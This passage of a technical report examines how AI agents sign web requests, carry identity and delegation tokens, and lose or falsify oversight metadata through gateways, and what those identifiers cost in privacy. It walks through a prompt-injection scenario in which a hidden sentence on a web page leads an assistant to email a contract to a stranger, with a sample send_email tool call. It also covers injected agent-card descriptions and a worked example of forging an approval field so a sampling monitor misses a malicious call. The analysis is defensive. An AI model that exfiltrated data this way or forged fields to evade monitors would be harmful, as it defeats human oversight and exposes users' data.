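Host: supplier.example
User-Agent: desk-assistant/3.1
Signature-Agent: "https://desk-assistant.example"
Signature-Input: sig=("@authority" "signature-agent");created=1796115604;
    expires=1796115664;keyid="poqk...";tag="web-bot-auth"
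Signature: sig=:u7Kx...:
```

Here `@authority` stands for the supplier's domain. An impostor could copy the `Signature-Agent` line but couldn't produce a matching signature without the secret key. Someone who intercepted the whole request couldn't reuse its signature on another site, or on this one after the minute had passed. The domain in `Signature-Agent` is therefore verified, while `User-Agent` is still self-reported.

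The signature in this example doesn't cover the page requested or the contents of a form. If the false tip had carried a signature like this, the Philadelphia police could have confirmed that Anthropic's software had contacted their site, but not what it had submitted. HTTP Message Signatures can also cover a hash of the contents, which would have let the police confirm the submission too.

A valid signature proves only that the visitor holds the key for a certain domain, and anyone can buy a domain. It doesn't identify the employee, and it gives the supplier no reason to trust the company. A separate IETF draft, *Registry and Signature Agent card* (2026), would let an operator publish a description of its agent, with its identity, purpose, expected request rate and keys. Its fields come from an existing registry that includes contact addresses, so a website could find out whom to contact.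 The operator would write this description itself, and "purpose" would describe the agent in general, not the task behind a particular visit.

### Status and early users

Meunier (2025) announced the first drafts in May 2025. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many of the internet's technical standards, set up a working group that originally aimed to submit a specification for approval by April 2026 but missed that date. The group's current text, *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (Meunier and Major, 2026), is dated 1 September 2026. It is a working-group draft intended to become a standard, so it has more backing than an individual's Internet-Draft, but the IETF hasn't approved it and its details may change.

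Some companies already identify their agents to websites without waiting for a standard to be approved. Willison (2025) logged a visit by OpenAI's ChatGPT agent, which operates a web browser for its user, and found that it identified itself in its headers. Cloudflare's *Bot Information for AGI Agent* lists the key directory of an agent from AGI, Inc. that makes purchases for people. Cloudflare classes the agent's access as "intermediary", meaning that end users can control what it does. This classification is useful to a monitor because such an agent's signature identifies the company that runs it, not the person who chose the action.

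These examples show that signing works in real products, but not what share of agent traffic is signed. A website would need to know that share before treating an unsigned visitor as suspicious.

### Agent cards

An agent may also ask another agent to do something instead of reading a web page. Suppose the supplier runs a sales agent, and the employee's assistant asks it for a quote. The two could use Agent2Agent (A2A), an open protocol for such requests that reached version 1.0 in March 2026. The sales agent would publish an agent card, a description of itself at a fixed address on the supplier's domain. In shortened form it might look like this:

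```json
{
  "name": "Supplier sales agent",
  "provider": {"organization": "Supplier Ltd", "url": "https://supplier.example"},
  "version": "1.4",
  "supportedInterfaces": [{"url": "https://supplier.example/a2a"}],
  "skills": [{"id": "quote-prices"}, {"id": "place-order"}],
  "signatures": [{"protected": "eyJh...", "signature": "Qk9x..."}]
}
```

Unlike tool calls, the card has a field for the operator, but it describes only the agent that receives the request. The supplier therefore gets no card for the employee's assistant and has to identify the assistant by whatever credential it presents.

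The `signatures` field is optional. As with signed tool definitions, the publisher puts the card's contents into a fixed order before signing them. The signature block identifies the public key the client needs to check the signature and can include an address for that key.

*A2A v1.0* (Ghumare, 2026) describes two attacks on cards. An attacker can copy a trusted agent's card and change only the address to which clients send requests. Or the attacker can put instructions in the card's descriptions, which the client's model may read. A signature exposes any change to the original card, but an attacker can sign the altered copy with their own key. The client must therefore check that the key belongs to the supplier, and then decide whether to trust the supplier with the task.

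### Pausing for authorisation

If the assistant then asks the sales agent to order 40 pallets, the sales agent may need someone's approval. A2A lets it stop partway through a task and ask:

```json
{
  "id": "task-88",
  "status": {
    "state": "TASK_STATE_AUTH_REQUIRED",
    "message": {
      "messageId": "msg-4",
      "role": "ROLE_AGENT",
      "parts": [{"text": "Ordering 40 pallets requires the buyer's approval."}]
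    }
  }
}
```

The assistant can put its own task into the same state and pass the question on until it reaches a person. This helps oversight because the approval can come from someone who knows why the task exists.

A2A's working draft states that the protocol doesn't define the scope, form, validity or revocation of an authorisation that someone gives in this state. *Agent Identity and Task-Based Access Control*, from AGNTCY, an open-source project that makes identity software for agents, quotes this passage and treats the omission as deliberate. Companies' rules differ, so A2A leaves the definition to the agent's own software, to whoever issues the credential, or to an extension of the protocol.

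If the employee approves the order, the protocol has no standard way to record whether the approval covers 40 pallets or any order, how long it lasts, or how the employee can withdraw it. A2A does specify that entering the state doesn't by itself authorise anything, and that an agent must not assume a credential it obtained this way covers later messages in the same task.

An A2A request also has no field for the requested operation. The assistant writes "order 40 pallets" in ordinary text, and the sales agent has to infer which of its skills to use. Software that enforces rules between the two companies therefore has no operation name to check, whereas an MCP call would include one. AGNTCY suggests an extension in which the caller declares the operation. The declaration could only narrow what the caller may do, since otherwise a caller could claim any authority.

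### Naming the person and the agent

Access tokens often identify either a person or a program. If the assistant uses the employee's own login, the supplier can't distinguish the employee's actions from the assistant's. If it uses an account of its own, the supplier doesn't learn for whom it acts. A delegation token would name both. The following sketch adapts an example from AGNTCY to the order, with a made-up limit on its size:

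```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.buyer.example",
  "sub": "employee-4471",
  "act": {"sub": "desk-assistant"},
  "exp": 1796119200,
  "cnf": {"jkt": "0ZcO..."},
  "a2a": {"taskId": "task-88"},
  "authorization_details": [{
    "type": "agentic_task",
    "actions": ["place-order"],
    "locations": ["https://supplier.example/a2a"],
    "max_pallets": 40
  }]
}
```

`iss` is the login system that issued and signed the token, `sub` is the person, and `act` is the agent acting for that person. `exp` is the expiry time, here an hour after the price request. `cnf` ties the token to the assistant's key, so a thief who copied the token couldn't use it without that key. The last two fields limit the token to one task and one kind of action.

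If the sales agent passed the order to a warehouse agent, the login system could issue a new token with the sales agent in `act` and the assistant nested inside it. The warehouse agent would receive the whole chain, from the employee to the sales agent. Each new token should allow only actions that the previous one allowed, because otherwise an agent could gain authority by passing a request along.

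A similar token could have stopped the theft of the contract by allowing the assistant to send email only to addresses at the employee's firm. The mail server could then have refused the message to the stranger without determining how the hidden sentence had affected the model. An investigator could also have read from the token whose agent it was and what the firm had allowed it to do. The supplier's web server would still have received none of this information, since nobody would normally send it the token.

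AGNTCY doesn't issue tokens of this kind yet. Its current software lets an administrator list the tools an agent may call and require approval for some of them. When approval is required, a person receives a notification with the caller, the recipient and the tool. These permissions stay the same whatever task the agent is working on. To justify tying authority to the task instead, AGNTCY cites recent security evaluations by OpenAI and Anthropic in which agents pursued legitimate objectives in illegitimate ways.

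### From research proposals to products

In 2024, before agents were common, Alan Chan and colleagues proposed giving an identifier to each running instance of an AI system, such as a single chat session, and linking it to information that outsiders could look up. They wanted investigators to know whom to investigate after an incident, and website operators to know whom to contact about a malfunctioning system. In 2025, Tobin South and colleagues proposed extending OAuth and OpenID Connect, the standards behind most web logins, with credentials that record which agent a person has authorised and for what.

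Companies have since built identification systems that are broader and less precise than an identifier for each instance. Web Bot Auth identifies an operator's domain, and an A2A card identifies a service. AGNTCY gives each registered agent an identifier and a signed "badge", which another company can verify without a prior agreement. None of these alone would distinguish the employee's session from a colleague's session with the same assistant. An investigator would still need an end-user identifier or a trace to do that.

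A draft called Client ID Metadata Documents also lets a program that connects to tools use a web address as its identifier. The service it contacts fetches a description and public keys from that address. MCP's July 2026 specification recommends this method when the two sides haven't already registered with each other. With it, the employee's app could prove to a tool server that it controls its maker's domain, but the `clientInfo` name in each call is still self-reported.

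In February 2026, the US standards agency NIST launched an initiative on standards for AI agents, and its cybersecurity centre published a concept paper on how organisations could apply existing identity standards to them. The paper's topics include linking an agent to the person who authorised it and recording the agent's actions. The paper is a project proposal issued for comment, so it doesn't oblige anyone to adopt a particular token or identifier.

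### Who gets to decide which agents are welcome

Meunier and Major work at Cloudflare and Google, and critics of Web Bot Auth worry that large network companies will become gatekeepers. The protocol doesn't require gatekeepers, since any operator can publish a key and any website can check a signature without a central authority's approval. But a small supplier is unlikely to write its own software for checking signatures and deciding which domains to trust. It will probably rely on the company that already protects its site. That company could then block an agent from thousands of sites by omitting it from the list of verified agents, even if the agent's signature is valid.

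The working group's original brief called for particular attention to barriers against new bots and new sites, and for a design without new choke points. A technical standard can only partly achieve this, because it can't make a network company list a newcomer or explain a refusal. Public criteria for listing and a way to appeal refusals would help more.

Small developers can afford a domain and a key, but they have difficulty earning a reputation for that domain and, in some cases, keeping the key secret. If a volunteer publishes a free agent that people run on their own laptops, shipping one shared key with the program would give the key to everyone, including impostors. Each user could instead sign with a separate key and domain, but websites would then receive requests from thousands of unknown operators. A hosted signing service could solve the problem, though everyone's requests would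 have to pass through another intermediary.

Signing also makes agents easier to block for websites that don't want them, which gives operators a reason to stop signing. Shops may treat agents that make purchases better because they want customers, but an agent that only reads pages has less to offer a site.

Malicious agents won't sign their requests, or will sign with a newly bought domain. Signatures would stop the impostors in GreyNoise's study from passing as ClaudeBot if websites checked them. But the software that sent the fake ClaudeBot requests had used more than 1,500 user-agent strings over 90 days, most of them the names of ordinary browsers. If false crawler names stopped working, its operators could keep using browser names. Websites can't refuse all unsigned requests, because human readers don't sign theirs.

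Signing is therefore a poor defence against attackers, but it suits cases where a known company has lost track of its own agents. OpenAI and Anthropic had no reason to hide from the Australian government or the Philadelphia police. Such a company could have its network equipment sign every outgoing request, so that the model couldn't leave the signature out. The signature can still be lost when an agent works through another service. The scanning service in Transluce's investigation made its own requests to the target websites, so they would have received a signature from the agent's request only if the service had passed it on.

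## How metadata is lost, changed or falsified in transit

Suppose the employee's app sends its request through a gateway, which passes it to one of Anthropic's Claude models instead of an OpenAI model. Anthropic's format has different fields, so the gateway has to rewrite the request. The rewritten request may lack both the employee's code, `9f2c41d07a`, which was in `safety_identifier`, and the label `purchasing`, which was in `metadata`.

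Bifrost's *Anthropic*, a guide to how one gateway program handles this translation, explains that the older `user` field becomes Anthropic's `metadata.user_id`. The guide has no entry for the newer `safety_identifier` field. A deployer that followed OpenAI's advice to switch to the newer field could therefore lose the identifier that the older one would have preserved.

### What survives a translation

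The table covers three documented routes. Bifrost converts OpenAI's format to Anthropic's. Anthropic's compatibility service accepts requests in OpenAI's format. LiteLLM, another gateway program, also converts in the opposite direction, from Anthropic's format to OpenAI's Responses API, as its *v1/messages → /responses Parameter Mapping* describes.

| Field | Route | What happens | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
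| `user` | Bifrost | Becomes `metadata.user_id` | Survives |
| `user` and `metadata` | Anthropic | Ignored | Lost |
| `metadata.user_id` | LiteLLM | Cut to 64 characters, then sent as both `user` and `prompt_cache_key` | Changed |
| `tool_call_id` | Anthropic | Accepted | Survives |
| Role of tool results | Bifrost | Consecutive results go into one `user` message | Changed |
| `system` and `developer` roles | Anthropic | All such messages become one, at the start | Changed |
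| `name` of a message's author | Anthropic | Ignored | Lost |
| Model's earlier reasoning | LiteLLM | Becomes ordinary model output | Changed |
| `strict`, which holds a tool's arguments to their declared format | Bifrost | Dropped | Lost |
| Status `incomplete` | LiteLLM | Becomes `max_tokens` | Changed |
| `refusal` text in the reply | Anthropic | Always empty | Lost |

Some of these changes matter more to a monitor than to the model. When Bifrost moves the supplier's page into a `user` message, the page is still marked as a tool result, so the model can tell it apart from the employee's words, but monitoring software that reads only the role would attribute the hidden sentence to the employee. When Anthropic joins the `system` and `developer` messages, an instruction that the deployer added halfway through a conversation moves to the beginning, and the combined message no longer shows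 when that instruction took effect.

Records of safety decisions can also be lost. On LiteLLM's route, the reply can give only three reasons for stopping: the model called a tool, reached its length limit, or finished normally. If a filter cut an answer short, the deployer's log would show one of those reasons instead. Bifrost's list of converted stop reasons has no entry for Anthropic's `refusal`.

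### An identifier that was too long

*AI Gateway*, a bug report by a user of Vercel's gateway, describes a less obvious failure. The user had given the gateway their own OpenAI key and was sending requests in Anthropic's format. The gateway copied Anthropic's `user_id` unchanged into OpenAI's `safety_identifier`, which accepted at most 64 characters. In tests on 1 August 2026, a 64-character value worked, but OpenAI returned an error for 65 characters. The gateway then resent the request under Vercel's own credential, and the user received an answer with a normal success code.

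Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, attaches a `user_id` of about 158 characters to every request, so all its requests on this route failed under the user's key. The bug report is mainly about the resulting charges to the user's Vercel credit, but the bigger problem for a monitor is that OpenAI would have recorded the requests under Vercel's account. OpenAI accepted the second attempt, so the gateway had presumably shortened or removed the identifier as well. The user could discover the switch to Vercel's account only by looking up individual requests. These details come from one person's report. OpenAI's reference page now gives a limit of 128 characters, which Claude Code's value would still exceed.

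LiteLLM avoids the error by cutting the value to its first 64 characters, which changes what it identifies. Claude Code's `user_id` contains a device ID, an account ID and a session ID, in that order, and the cut value keeps the whole device ID but none of the account ID. Two colleagues who share a computer would therefore have the same code, and one person with two computers would have two codes. LiteLLM doesn't cut the value in requests with stop sequences (strings at which the model stops writing), which it handles by a different route, so the provider could receive two codes for one person on one computer.

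The bug report suggests hashing the value instead. The hash would fit the limit, but if it covered the whole value, it would change with every new session ID, and the provider couldn't link an account's requests across sessions. To avoid this, the gateway would have to hash only the account ID, so it would need to know how each client builds its identifier.

### Fields that gateways remove or add

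Gateways also drop fields deliberately, because a provider may reject a request that contains something it doesn't recognise. LiteLLM removes undocumented keys from `metadata` before sending a request to Anthropic, according to the title of a merged code change (CodSpeed, *fix(anthropic): strip undocumented keys from metadata before sending to API*), so a `team` label would not get through. Bifrost silently drops unknown beta headers, which turn on experimental features, when it sends Claude requests to Google's, Amazon's or Microsoft's cloud. The stated purpose is to prevent errors. Unlike a rejected request, which customers notice immediately, a missing label may go unnoticed until an investigation.

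A gateway can also add better metadata than it received. Cloudflare's *Custom metadata* describes a gateway that logs a deployer's own labels with each request. If an employee logs in through Cloudflare's access service, the gateway adds a verified user ID as `cf.user_id`. It deletes any label beginning with `cf.` that the deployer sent, so the deployer can't forge the ID.

The gateway holds up to five custom labels per request. If a request already has five, Cloudflare may remove the last to make room for the user ID (`cf.user_id`). A verified ID is usually more useful than a self-reported label, but a deployer that put its trace ID last would lose the link to its other records. An agent that connects with a service credential instead of a person's login gets no `cf.user_id`.

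The simplest way to avoid translation losses is to send requests in a format the provider already accepts. LiteLLM has a setting that forwards a request in Anthropic's format to a provider that accepts it, even if LiteLLM would normally convert it. Deployers that rely on a particular field could also send a test request with a known value and ask the provider whether the value arrived.

### Which model answered

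The provider's name in a log may be wrong, so OpenTelemetry suggests using the requested model, the answering model and the server's address to identify the system. These clues are weaker behind a gateway, because the address is the gateway's own and the gateway controls the name of the answering model.

*What the Middleman Delivers* (Wu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) compared answers from 20 gateways with answers obtained directly from OpenAI and Anthropic. In the first round, nine gateways performed noticeably differently on at least one model, and seven of those nine were among the ten that charged less than the official price. The researchers couldn't tell whether a gateway had substituted a cheaper model, added instructions or changed a setting. The model names the gateways returned mostly matched the request, so a monitor that checked only this field would have missed the differences.

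Even the recorded amount of text can be unreliable. For identical requests, five gateways reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official service did. Hidden instructions or altered accounting could explain the extra tokens. Wu and colleagues could check the account balance at only one of these gateways, and there the customer paid for the extra tokens.

### When wrong metadata is worse than none

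*LDP* (Prakash, March 2026) tested the LLM Delegate Protocol, a proposed way for AI agents to pass tasks to each other. The protocol's messages describe the model behind each agent, including the model's speed, cost and expected quality. Each answer can also include a confidence score and a record of whether anyone verified it.

One experiment used 15 tasks in which a model had to combine the answers of three other models. In one version it also received accurate confidence data, and in another it received none. In a third, one answer had a falsely high confidence of 0.99 and was marked as having passed verification. Another model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, graded the results from 1 to 10.

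| Metadata with the answers | Average grade | Standard deviation |
|---|---|---|
| Accurate | 7.65 | 1.21 |
| None | 7.85 | 1.84 |
| One false record | 6.85 | 2.66 |

Accurate metadata didn't help, and a false record appears to have done harm. But the one-point gap could easily be chance, because with 15 tasks and such variable grades, its standard error is roughly 0.8 if the grades are independent. Prakash concludes that protocols should pair confidence scores with verification fields. However, a `verified` field is still self-reported unless the receiver can check who did the verifying, and the false record in this experiment already had such a field with a false value.

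Other metadata saved time or tokens. When the protocol's descriptions let a router send easy tasks to the smallest model, those tasks took 2.9 seconds instead of 34.8. But across all tasks, the new protocol was slower on average than the A2A-style baseline, and its answers were no better. Putting instructions into labelled fields instead of prose reduced the number of tokens by 37%, with no visible loss of quality. The paper also reports a 96% detection rate for unauthorised requests, but this comes from a simulation that mostly reflects which fields each protocol has.

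A follow-up paper, *The Provenance Paradox in Multi-Agent LLM Routing* (Prakash, 2026), examined agents that exaggerate their own quality to attract work. In a simulation with ten agents, three of them dishonest, choosing the agent with the highest claimed quality gave an average result of 0.55, compared with 0.68 for choosing at random and 0.95 for choosing by true quality. Choosing by claimed quality did worse than choosing at random in 10 of the 36 versions tested, mainly those with many dishonest agents and large exaggerations. It also did worse in a test with real Claude models, scoring 8.90 against 9.30, but that test had only ten tasks, and choosing by verified quality also scored 9.30.

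These studies measured answer quality, not whether a monitor caught misuse, so their numbers don't apply to safety monitoring, though the mechanism probably does. Suppose, with invented figures, that an agent makes 1,000 tool calls a day, one of them malicious, and a monitor can inspect 100. If it picks them at random, it has a 10% chance of finding the malicious call. If 800 calls have a field marking them as approved by a person, and the monitor picks its 100 from the other 200, its chance rises to 50% if the malicious call lacks the field but falls to zero if the attacker filled it in.

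The monitor could guard against false marks by still inspecting some of the marked calls. If it spent 20 of its 100 inspections on them, it would have a 2.5% chance of catching a falsely marked call and a 40% chance of catching an unmarked one. An unverified field is safer for increasing scrutiny than for reducing it, because an attacker gains little by adding a field that attracts attention.

### Signing whole messages

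A gateway can change any message it forwards, but a signature can reveal the change. Sharif (2026), in *MCPS*, proposes signing every MCP message, in addition to the tool definitions that other schemes already sign. This is an individual's Internet-Draft, first published in March 2026 and revised in August, and not an approved standard. Under the proposal, the stray email's tool call would look roughly like this:

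```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 7, "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {"to": "stranger@elsewhere.example", "body": "..."},
    "_meta": {"traceparent": "00-7c1e5f0a..."}
  },
  "mcps": {
    "version": "1.0",
    "passport_id": "ap_5d0e...",
    "timestamp": "2026-12-01T09:00:09Z",
    "nonce": "e81b...",
    "signature": "Xk2v..."
  }
}
```

The app puts the message into a fixed order and computes its hash. It then signs the hash together with the time, a random number called a nonce, and the ID of its "passport", a signed document that links its key to its identity. The mail server repeats the calculation and checks the signature, which adds three things:

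- **Integrity.** If anyone between the app and the server changed the recipient or deleted the trace ID, the signature no longer matches.
- **Origin.** The signature ties the message to the app's key. How much this reveals about the app depends on who issued the passport, so a passport that the app signed itself gets the lowest trust level.
- **Replay protection.** If someone captures the message and sends it again, the server recognises the nonce. By default the server also rejects messages more than five minutes old, with a minute's allowance for inaccurate clocks.

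A signed message can also serve as evidence months later, if someone keeps the message and the public key. This would help if the mail server's operator and the app's maker disagreed about who had chosen the stranger's address.

Adoption would be difficult. Software that doesn't support the scheme ignores the `mcps` field, and a client may be set to continue without signatures if the server doesn't offer them. In the August draft, the client and server also agree on signing during an opening handshake, but MCP's July 2026 version treats every request as self-contained, so Sharif would probably have to redesign that part.

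Whole-message signatures also conflict with translation. Putting fields into a fixed order lets a signature survive changes in spacing or field order, but the signature still fails if a gateway changes `user` to `metadata.user_id`. *Rewriting the Response Path* (Luo, Zhang et al., 2026) notes that signing a whole response would make clients reject honest traffic that a gateway had only reformatted. It proposes that the model provider sign only the fields that determine what an agent does, such as the tool's name and arguments. In tests on a widely used gateway, the client rejected every response that had been tampered with and no honest ones. The client also records which routes use signatures, so a gateway can't avoid the check by removing them.

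For oversight, a similar scheme would also need to cover the end user's identifier, the trace ID and any trust labels. Otherwise a gateway could leave the action intact and change the record of who requested it.

### What a signature cannot add

As with signed tool definitions, a valid signature doesn't make the content true or safe. The signature on the stray email would be valid because the employee's app did send it. If a deployer signed an invented `safety_identifier` with every request, the provider could prove who had sent the false codes but still couldn't recognise the user. A thief with a stolen key could also sign anything.

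If the app never recorded that the recipient's address came from a web page, signing the message won't add that fact. But a valid signature over the whole message shows that the information was already missing when the app sent the message, so the investigator knows to ask the app's maker about the gap instead of searching the gateway for a fault.

### Does metadata matter without enforcement?

Some metadata fields are pointless without enforcement, because a program that breaks the rules can also ignore or falsify them. In the first round of their tests, Wu and colleagues sent requests with `tool_choice` set to `none`, which is meant to stop the model from calling tools. Four gateways still returned 30 tool calls in total, 24 of them from one gateway. The official services returned none, and neither did any gateway in the second round. The calls had no effect because the researchers' client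 never ran them. Wu and colleagues advise developers to enforce tool permissions in the client, which works whatever the gateway returns.

That kind of enforcement suits a simple rule, such as "run no tools". The employee's task needed `send_email`, so the app had to permit one email and refuse another. A program can enforce a rule against sending contracts to strangers only if it knows which addresses are approved and what is in the attachment. Without metadata that supplies these facts, the app could only allow or block all email. If the program relies on a field that passed through a gateway, it also needs a signature or another way to check the value.

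Enforcement can't help once the email has been sent, so an investigator depends on the records. Prakash designed the protocol's "delegation contracts" partly for this purpose. A contract states a task's goal, deadline and budget. In one example, an agent with a budget of 6,000 tokens uses 8,200. The client marks the contract as violated and keeps the output for inspection, but it can't recover the tokens. The contract makes the overrun visible if the agent reports its usage honestly.

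## What the added fields would cost in privacy

A field that helps an investigator follow the employee's task helps anyone else who obtains the record just as much. A provider could use `safety_identifier` to catch a repeat offender, but nothing in the field prevents the provider from also using it to compile a history of an honest person's questions.

### Four harms

Oversight metadata can harm the people it describes in four ways:

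- Identification: someone works out which person is behind a code.
- Linkage: someone connects a person's activity at different services or times, with or without a name.
- Inference: someone derives a sensitive fact that no field states, such as an illness from a series of questions about one drug.
- Exposure: a thief, a court or the police obtain records that a company kept for another purpose.

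Identification, linkage and inference resemble the tests that European regulators use to decide whether data is anonymous. The European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together the EU's national privacy authorities, sets out these tests in *Guidelines 02/2026 on Anonymisation* (2026), a draft for public consultation. They are whether any record is unique to one person, whether someone could match it with information held elsewhere, and whether it supports a specific, meaningful conclusion about an individual. Exposure makes the other harms more likely by giving more people access to the data. The EDPB lists rogue employees, cybercriminals and foreign intelligence agencies among those who might try to identify someone.

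The ratings below are rough judgements. They assume that each field contains only what its definition calls for.

| Field | Identification | Linkage | Inference | Exposure | Main reason |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| User code: plain hash of an email address | High | High | Medium | High | Anyone with a list of addresses can reverse it, and every company gets the same code |
| User code: random, different for each provider | Low | Medium | Medium | Medium | It joins one person's requests at one provider, but only the deployer has the name |
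| Age band or profession | Medium | Low | High | Medium | It states a personal fact, and a rare profession can single someone out |
| Trust label on a text | Low | Low | Low | Low | It describes the text |
| List of people who may read a text | Medium | Medium | Medium | Medium | It shows who works with whom |
| Tool's name, operator and hints | Low | Low | Medium | Low | A tool for booking clinic visits says something about its users |
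| Address of a page the model read | Low | Low | High | Medium | The address alone may reveal an illness or a legal problem |
| History stored in a photo | Medium | Medium | Medium | Medium | Times and device details can connect one person's files |
| Safety flag on a page | Low | Low | Low | Low | It concerns the page's owner, not its readers |
| Safety flag on a person | Medium | High | High | High | It records a suspicion, and sharing it needs a common identifier |
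| Trace ID | Low | Medium | Low | Medium | It joins companies' records of one task, but not one task to the next |
| Prompts and answers in a trace | High | Medium | High | High | People type names, addresses and medical details |
| Delegation token | High | High | Medium | High | It names the person to outside companies |
| Signature on a web request | Low | Low | Low | Low | It identifies a company, unless an individual signs with a personal domain |

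Fields that are harmless alone can be harmful in combination. The EDPB gives the example of a street where several people wear black suits and several walk dogs, but only one person does both. Combined fields in an AI provider's user profiles could single out a user in the same way. Suppose a platform has 10,000 users, spread evenly over 1,000 sign-up dates, five countries and four age bands. There are 20,000 possible combinations, so about six in ten users would have a combination that no other user shares.

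Leaving out the text of conversations removes much of the privacy risk, but the remaining records can still be linked to each other. A log with OpenTelemetry's default settings can show that someone returned to the same conversation at 3 a.m. on four nights, without showing what the conversation was about.

### Reversing a hashed email address

OpenAI's advice to hash the username or email address doesn't mention a secret key. Without one, a hash offers little protection, because anyone can compute it. Suppose an attacker has a billion email addresses from old data breaches and a computer that calculates a billion hashes a second. The attacker can hash the whole list in one second and look for the employee's hash among the results. If the employee's address is on the list, the match will identify it.

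Shortening the hash doesn't help much. The employee's code, `9f2c41d07a`, has ten characters with 16 possible values each, so there are about 1.1 trillion possible codes. The chance that any of the billion addresses matches it by accident is about one in 1,100. If the attacker knows where the employee works, and the firm has 400 staff and builds its addresses from first and last names, the attacker needs only a staff list and 400 guesses.

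The US consumer protection agency, the FTC, warned companies in 2024 not to treat hashed identifiers as anonymous. Its former chief technologist, Ed Felten, had shown in 2012 that someone could reverse the hash of a US social security number in less time than it takes to get a cup of coffee. The agency's staff now say it takes a few seconds.

The same plain hash also links people across companies without anyone reversing it. If the employee's firm sends `9f2c41d07a` to two AI providers, the providers can find the match by comparing their lists. In one such case, the FTC alleged that BetterHelp, an online counselling service, sent Facebook its users' hashed email addresses, knowing that Facebook would undo the hashing. Facebook allegedly learned who was seeking therapy and used this to target advertising. The optional email hash in Anthropic's user profiles has the same weakness if platforms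 fill it with plain hashes, because anyone with two platforms' records could match all their shared users, not only offenders.

### A different code for each provider

A deployer can avoid reversal by giving each employee a random code and keeping a table of codes and names. The code then has no mathematical connection to the address. The deployer can also use a keyed hash, which mixes a secret into the calculation:

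code = HMAC(secret key, employee number + provider + month)

HMAC is a standard method for computing such hashes. An attacker who has every employee number still can't test a guess without the key. Stibbe's *Key takeaways and insights from the EDPB Pseudonymisation Guidelines* calls keyed codes of this type stronger than a simple hash. The law firm Pinsent Masons reports that the EU's data protection supervisor and the Spanish regulator recommend a confidential key or a "salt", a value added to the data before hashing. A salt helps here only if it stays secret, because an attacker who knows it can run the billion guesses again in one more second.

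Including the provider and the month in the calculation produces unrelated codes for the same person:

| Method | Provider A, December | Provider B, December | Provider A, January |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain hash | `9f2c41d07a` | `9f2c41d07a` | `9f2c41d07a` |
| Keyed hash, one key for everything | `41be08c2f5` | `41be08c2f5` | `41be08c2f5` |
| Keyed hash, by provider | `d60a9371be` | `c07d52e814` | `d60a9371be` |
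| Keyed hash, by provider and month | `5a19f3b06c` | `e83c7d4a21` | `07f4c9be35` |

Each change limits a monitor in a different way. When a single keyed hash replaces a plain hash, the provider loses almost nothing, since it can still recognise a returning user. But the provider then depends on the deployer to name that user, and if the deployer loses its key or table, nobody can.

Separate codes for each provider also limit the damage of a breach. ICTRecht's *Pseudonymisation* says that when a company sends pseudonymised data outside the company and the recipient suffers a breach, the data stays protected as long as the key hasn't leaked too. But with separate codes, two providers can no longer discover that the same person divided a harmful project between them unless the deployer tells them.

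Replacing codes every month weakens oversight the most. Suppose a provider reviews anyone with six flagged requests, and someone sends one such request every Monday. A permanent code would lead to a review in the sixth week, but monthly codes never would, because no month has six Mondays. A ban on the December code also lapses in January unless the deployer carries it over. The deployer could prevent this by leaving a banned person's code unchanged. To detect flagged requests that continue across months, the provider could ask the deployer whether two suspicious codes belong to one person, which is slower but doesn't require everyone to have a permanent code.

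Rotation is also easy to undo by accident. A Chat Completions app resends earlier messages, so a conversation that runs past midnight on 31 December would arrive with the same text under both the old and new codes. A `prompt_cache_key` that the deployer sets for each user and never changes would also link the two codes. An employee who signs a message with their full name would be identifiable under any code.

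### When a code counts as personal data

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to information about an identified or identifiable person. A deployer might hope that using a code such as `5a19f3b06c` exempts the data, at least for the provider, which can't tell who the code refers to.

The leading case on this point began with a failed Spanish bank. The Single Resolution Board (SRB), the EU agency that handles failing banks, invited former shareholders and creditors of Banco Popular to comment on whether they should receive compensation. It passed some comments to the consultancy Deloitte with codes in place of names. Several people complained that the SRB hadn't told them that Deloitte would receive their data. The Court of Justice of the European Union's *Judgment of the Court in Case C-413/23 P* (2025) summarises the ruling of 4 September 2025, known as *EDPS v SRB*,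 which made two points that matter here:

- Coded data is not personal data for everyone in every case. If the codes effectively prevent a recipient from identifying anyone, the data may not be personal for that recipient.
- The SRB still had to tell people about Deloitte. That duty arose when it collected the comments, and at that time the SRB could identify the authors.

The case concerned the data protection law for EU institutions, but the EDPB applies its reasoning to the GDPR. A deployer that knows which employees the codes refer to would therefore probably have to tell them that an AI provider receives their data, even if the codes are meaningless to the provider.

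The ruling changed the regulators' position. Seven months earlier, the EDPB's *Pseudonymisation* (2025) had stated that coded data remains personal even when another party holds the key. The 2026 draft accepts that coded data can be personal for one company but not for another, but it defines identification broadly, as distinguishing someone from others in a way that makes it possible to treat them differently, even without a name.

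One of the draft's examples is close to an AI provider's situation. Several websites send an advertising company the pages that people visit, along with a code derived from each visitor's device. The company never receives a name, but it uses the codes to follow people between sites and choose their adverts. The EDPB concludes that these people are identified or identifiable for the advertising company. By the same reasoning, a provider that uses `safety_identifier` to block one user and serve another is probably handling personal data, even if the code is random. A keyed code makes abuse harder, but the GDPR probably still applies to the provider.

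Contracts between the companies may not change this. If the provider processes requests on the deployer's behalf, the draft requires the data to be assessed from the deployer's perspective, and the deployer knows the names. A contractual promise not to re-identify anyone also counts for less than a legal prohibition, because the parties can revise or ignore it.

The law could still change. In February 2026, Inside Privacy's *EDPB publishes report on stakeholder event on anonymisation and pseudonymisation* described the board's guidelines on pseudonymisation as ongoing work. EU lawmakers are negotiating a package of amendments to the GDPR. White reported in *EU member states finalize negotiating stance on Digital Omnibus* (October 2026) that national governments want to keep the current definition of personal data and add standards for pseudonymisation. They still have to agree on a text with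 the European Parliament.

In the United States, the FTC has focused on what companies tell their users. It brought a case against Premom, a fertility app that had promised to share only "non-identifiable data" but allegedly shared advertising and device identifiers that others could use to track people. A deployer that described plain email hashes as anonymous would risk a similar case.

### When others obtain the records

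In May 2025, a US court hearing the New York Times's copyright case against OpenAI ordered the company to preserve output data that it would otherwise have deleted, including ChatGPT conversations that users had deleted. The obligation to keep new data ended that September. The court later ordered OpenAI to give the plaintiffs 20 million ChatGPT conversations with identifying details removed. The users were not parties to the case, and they could not rely on a deletion setting to keep their conversations out of it.

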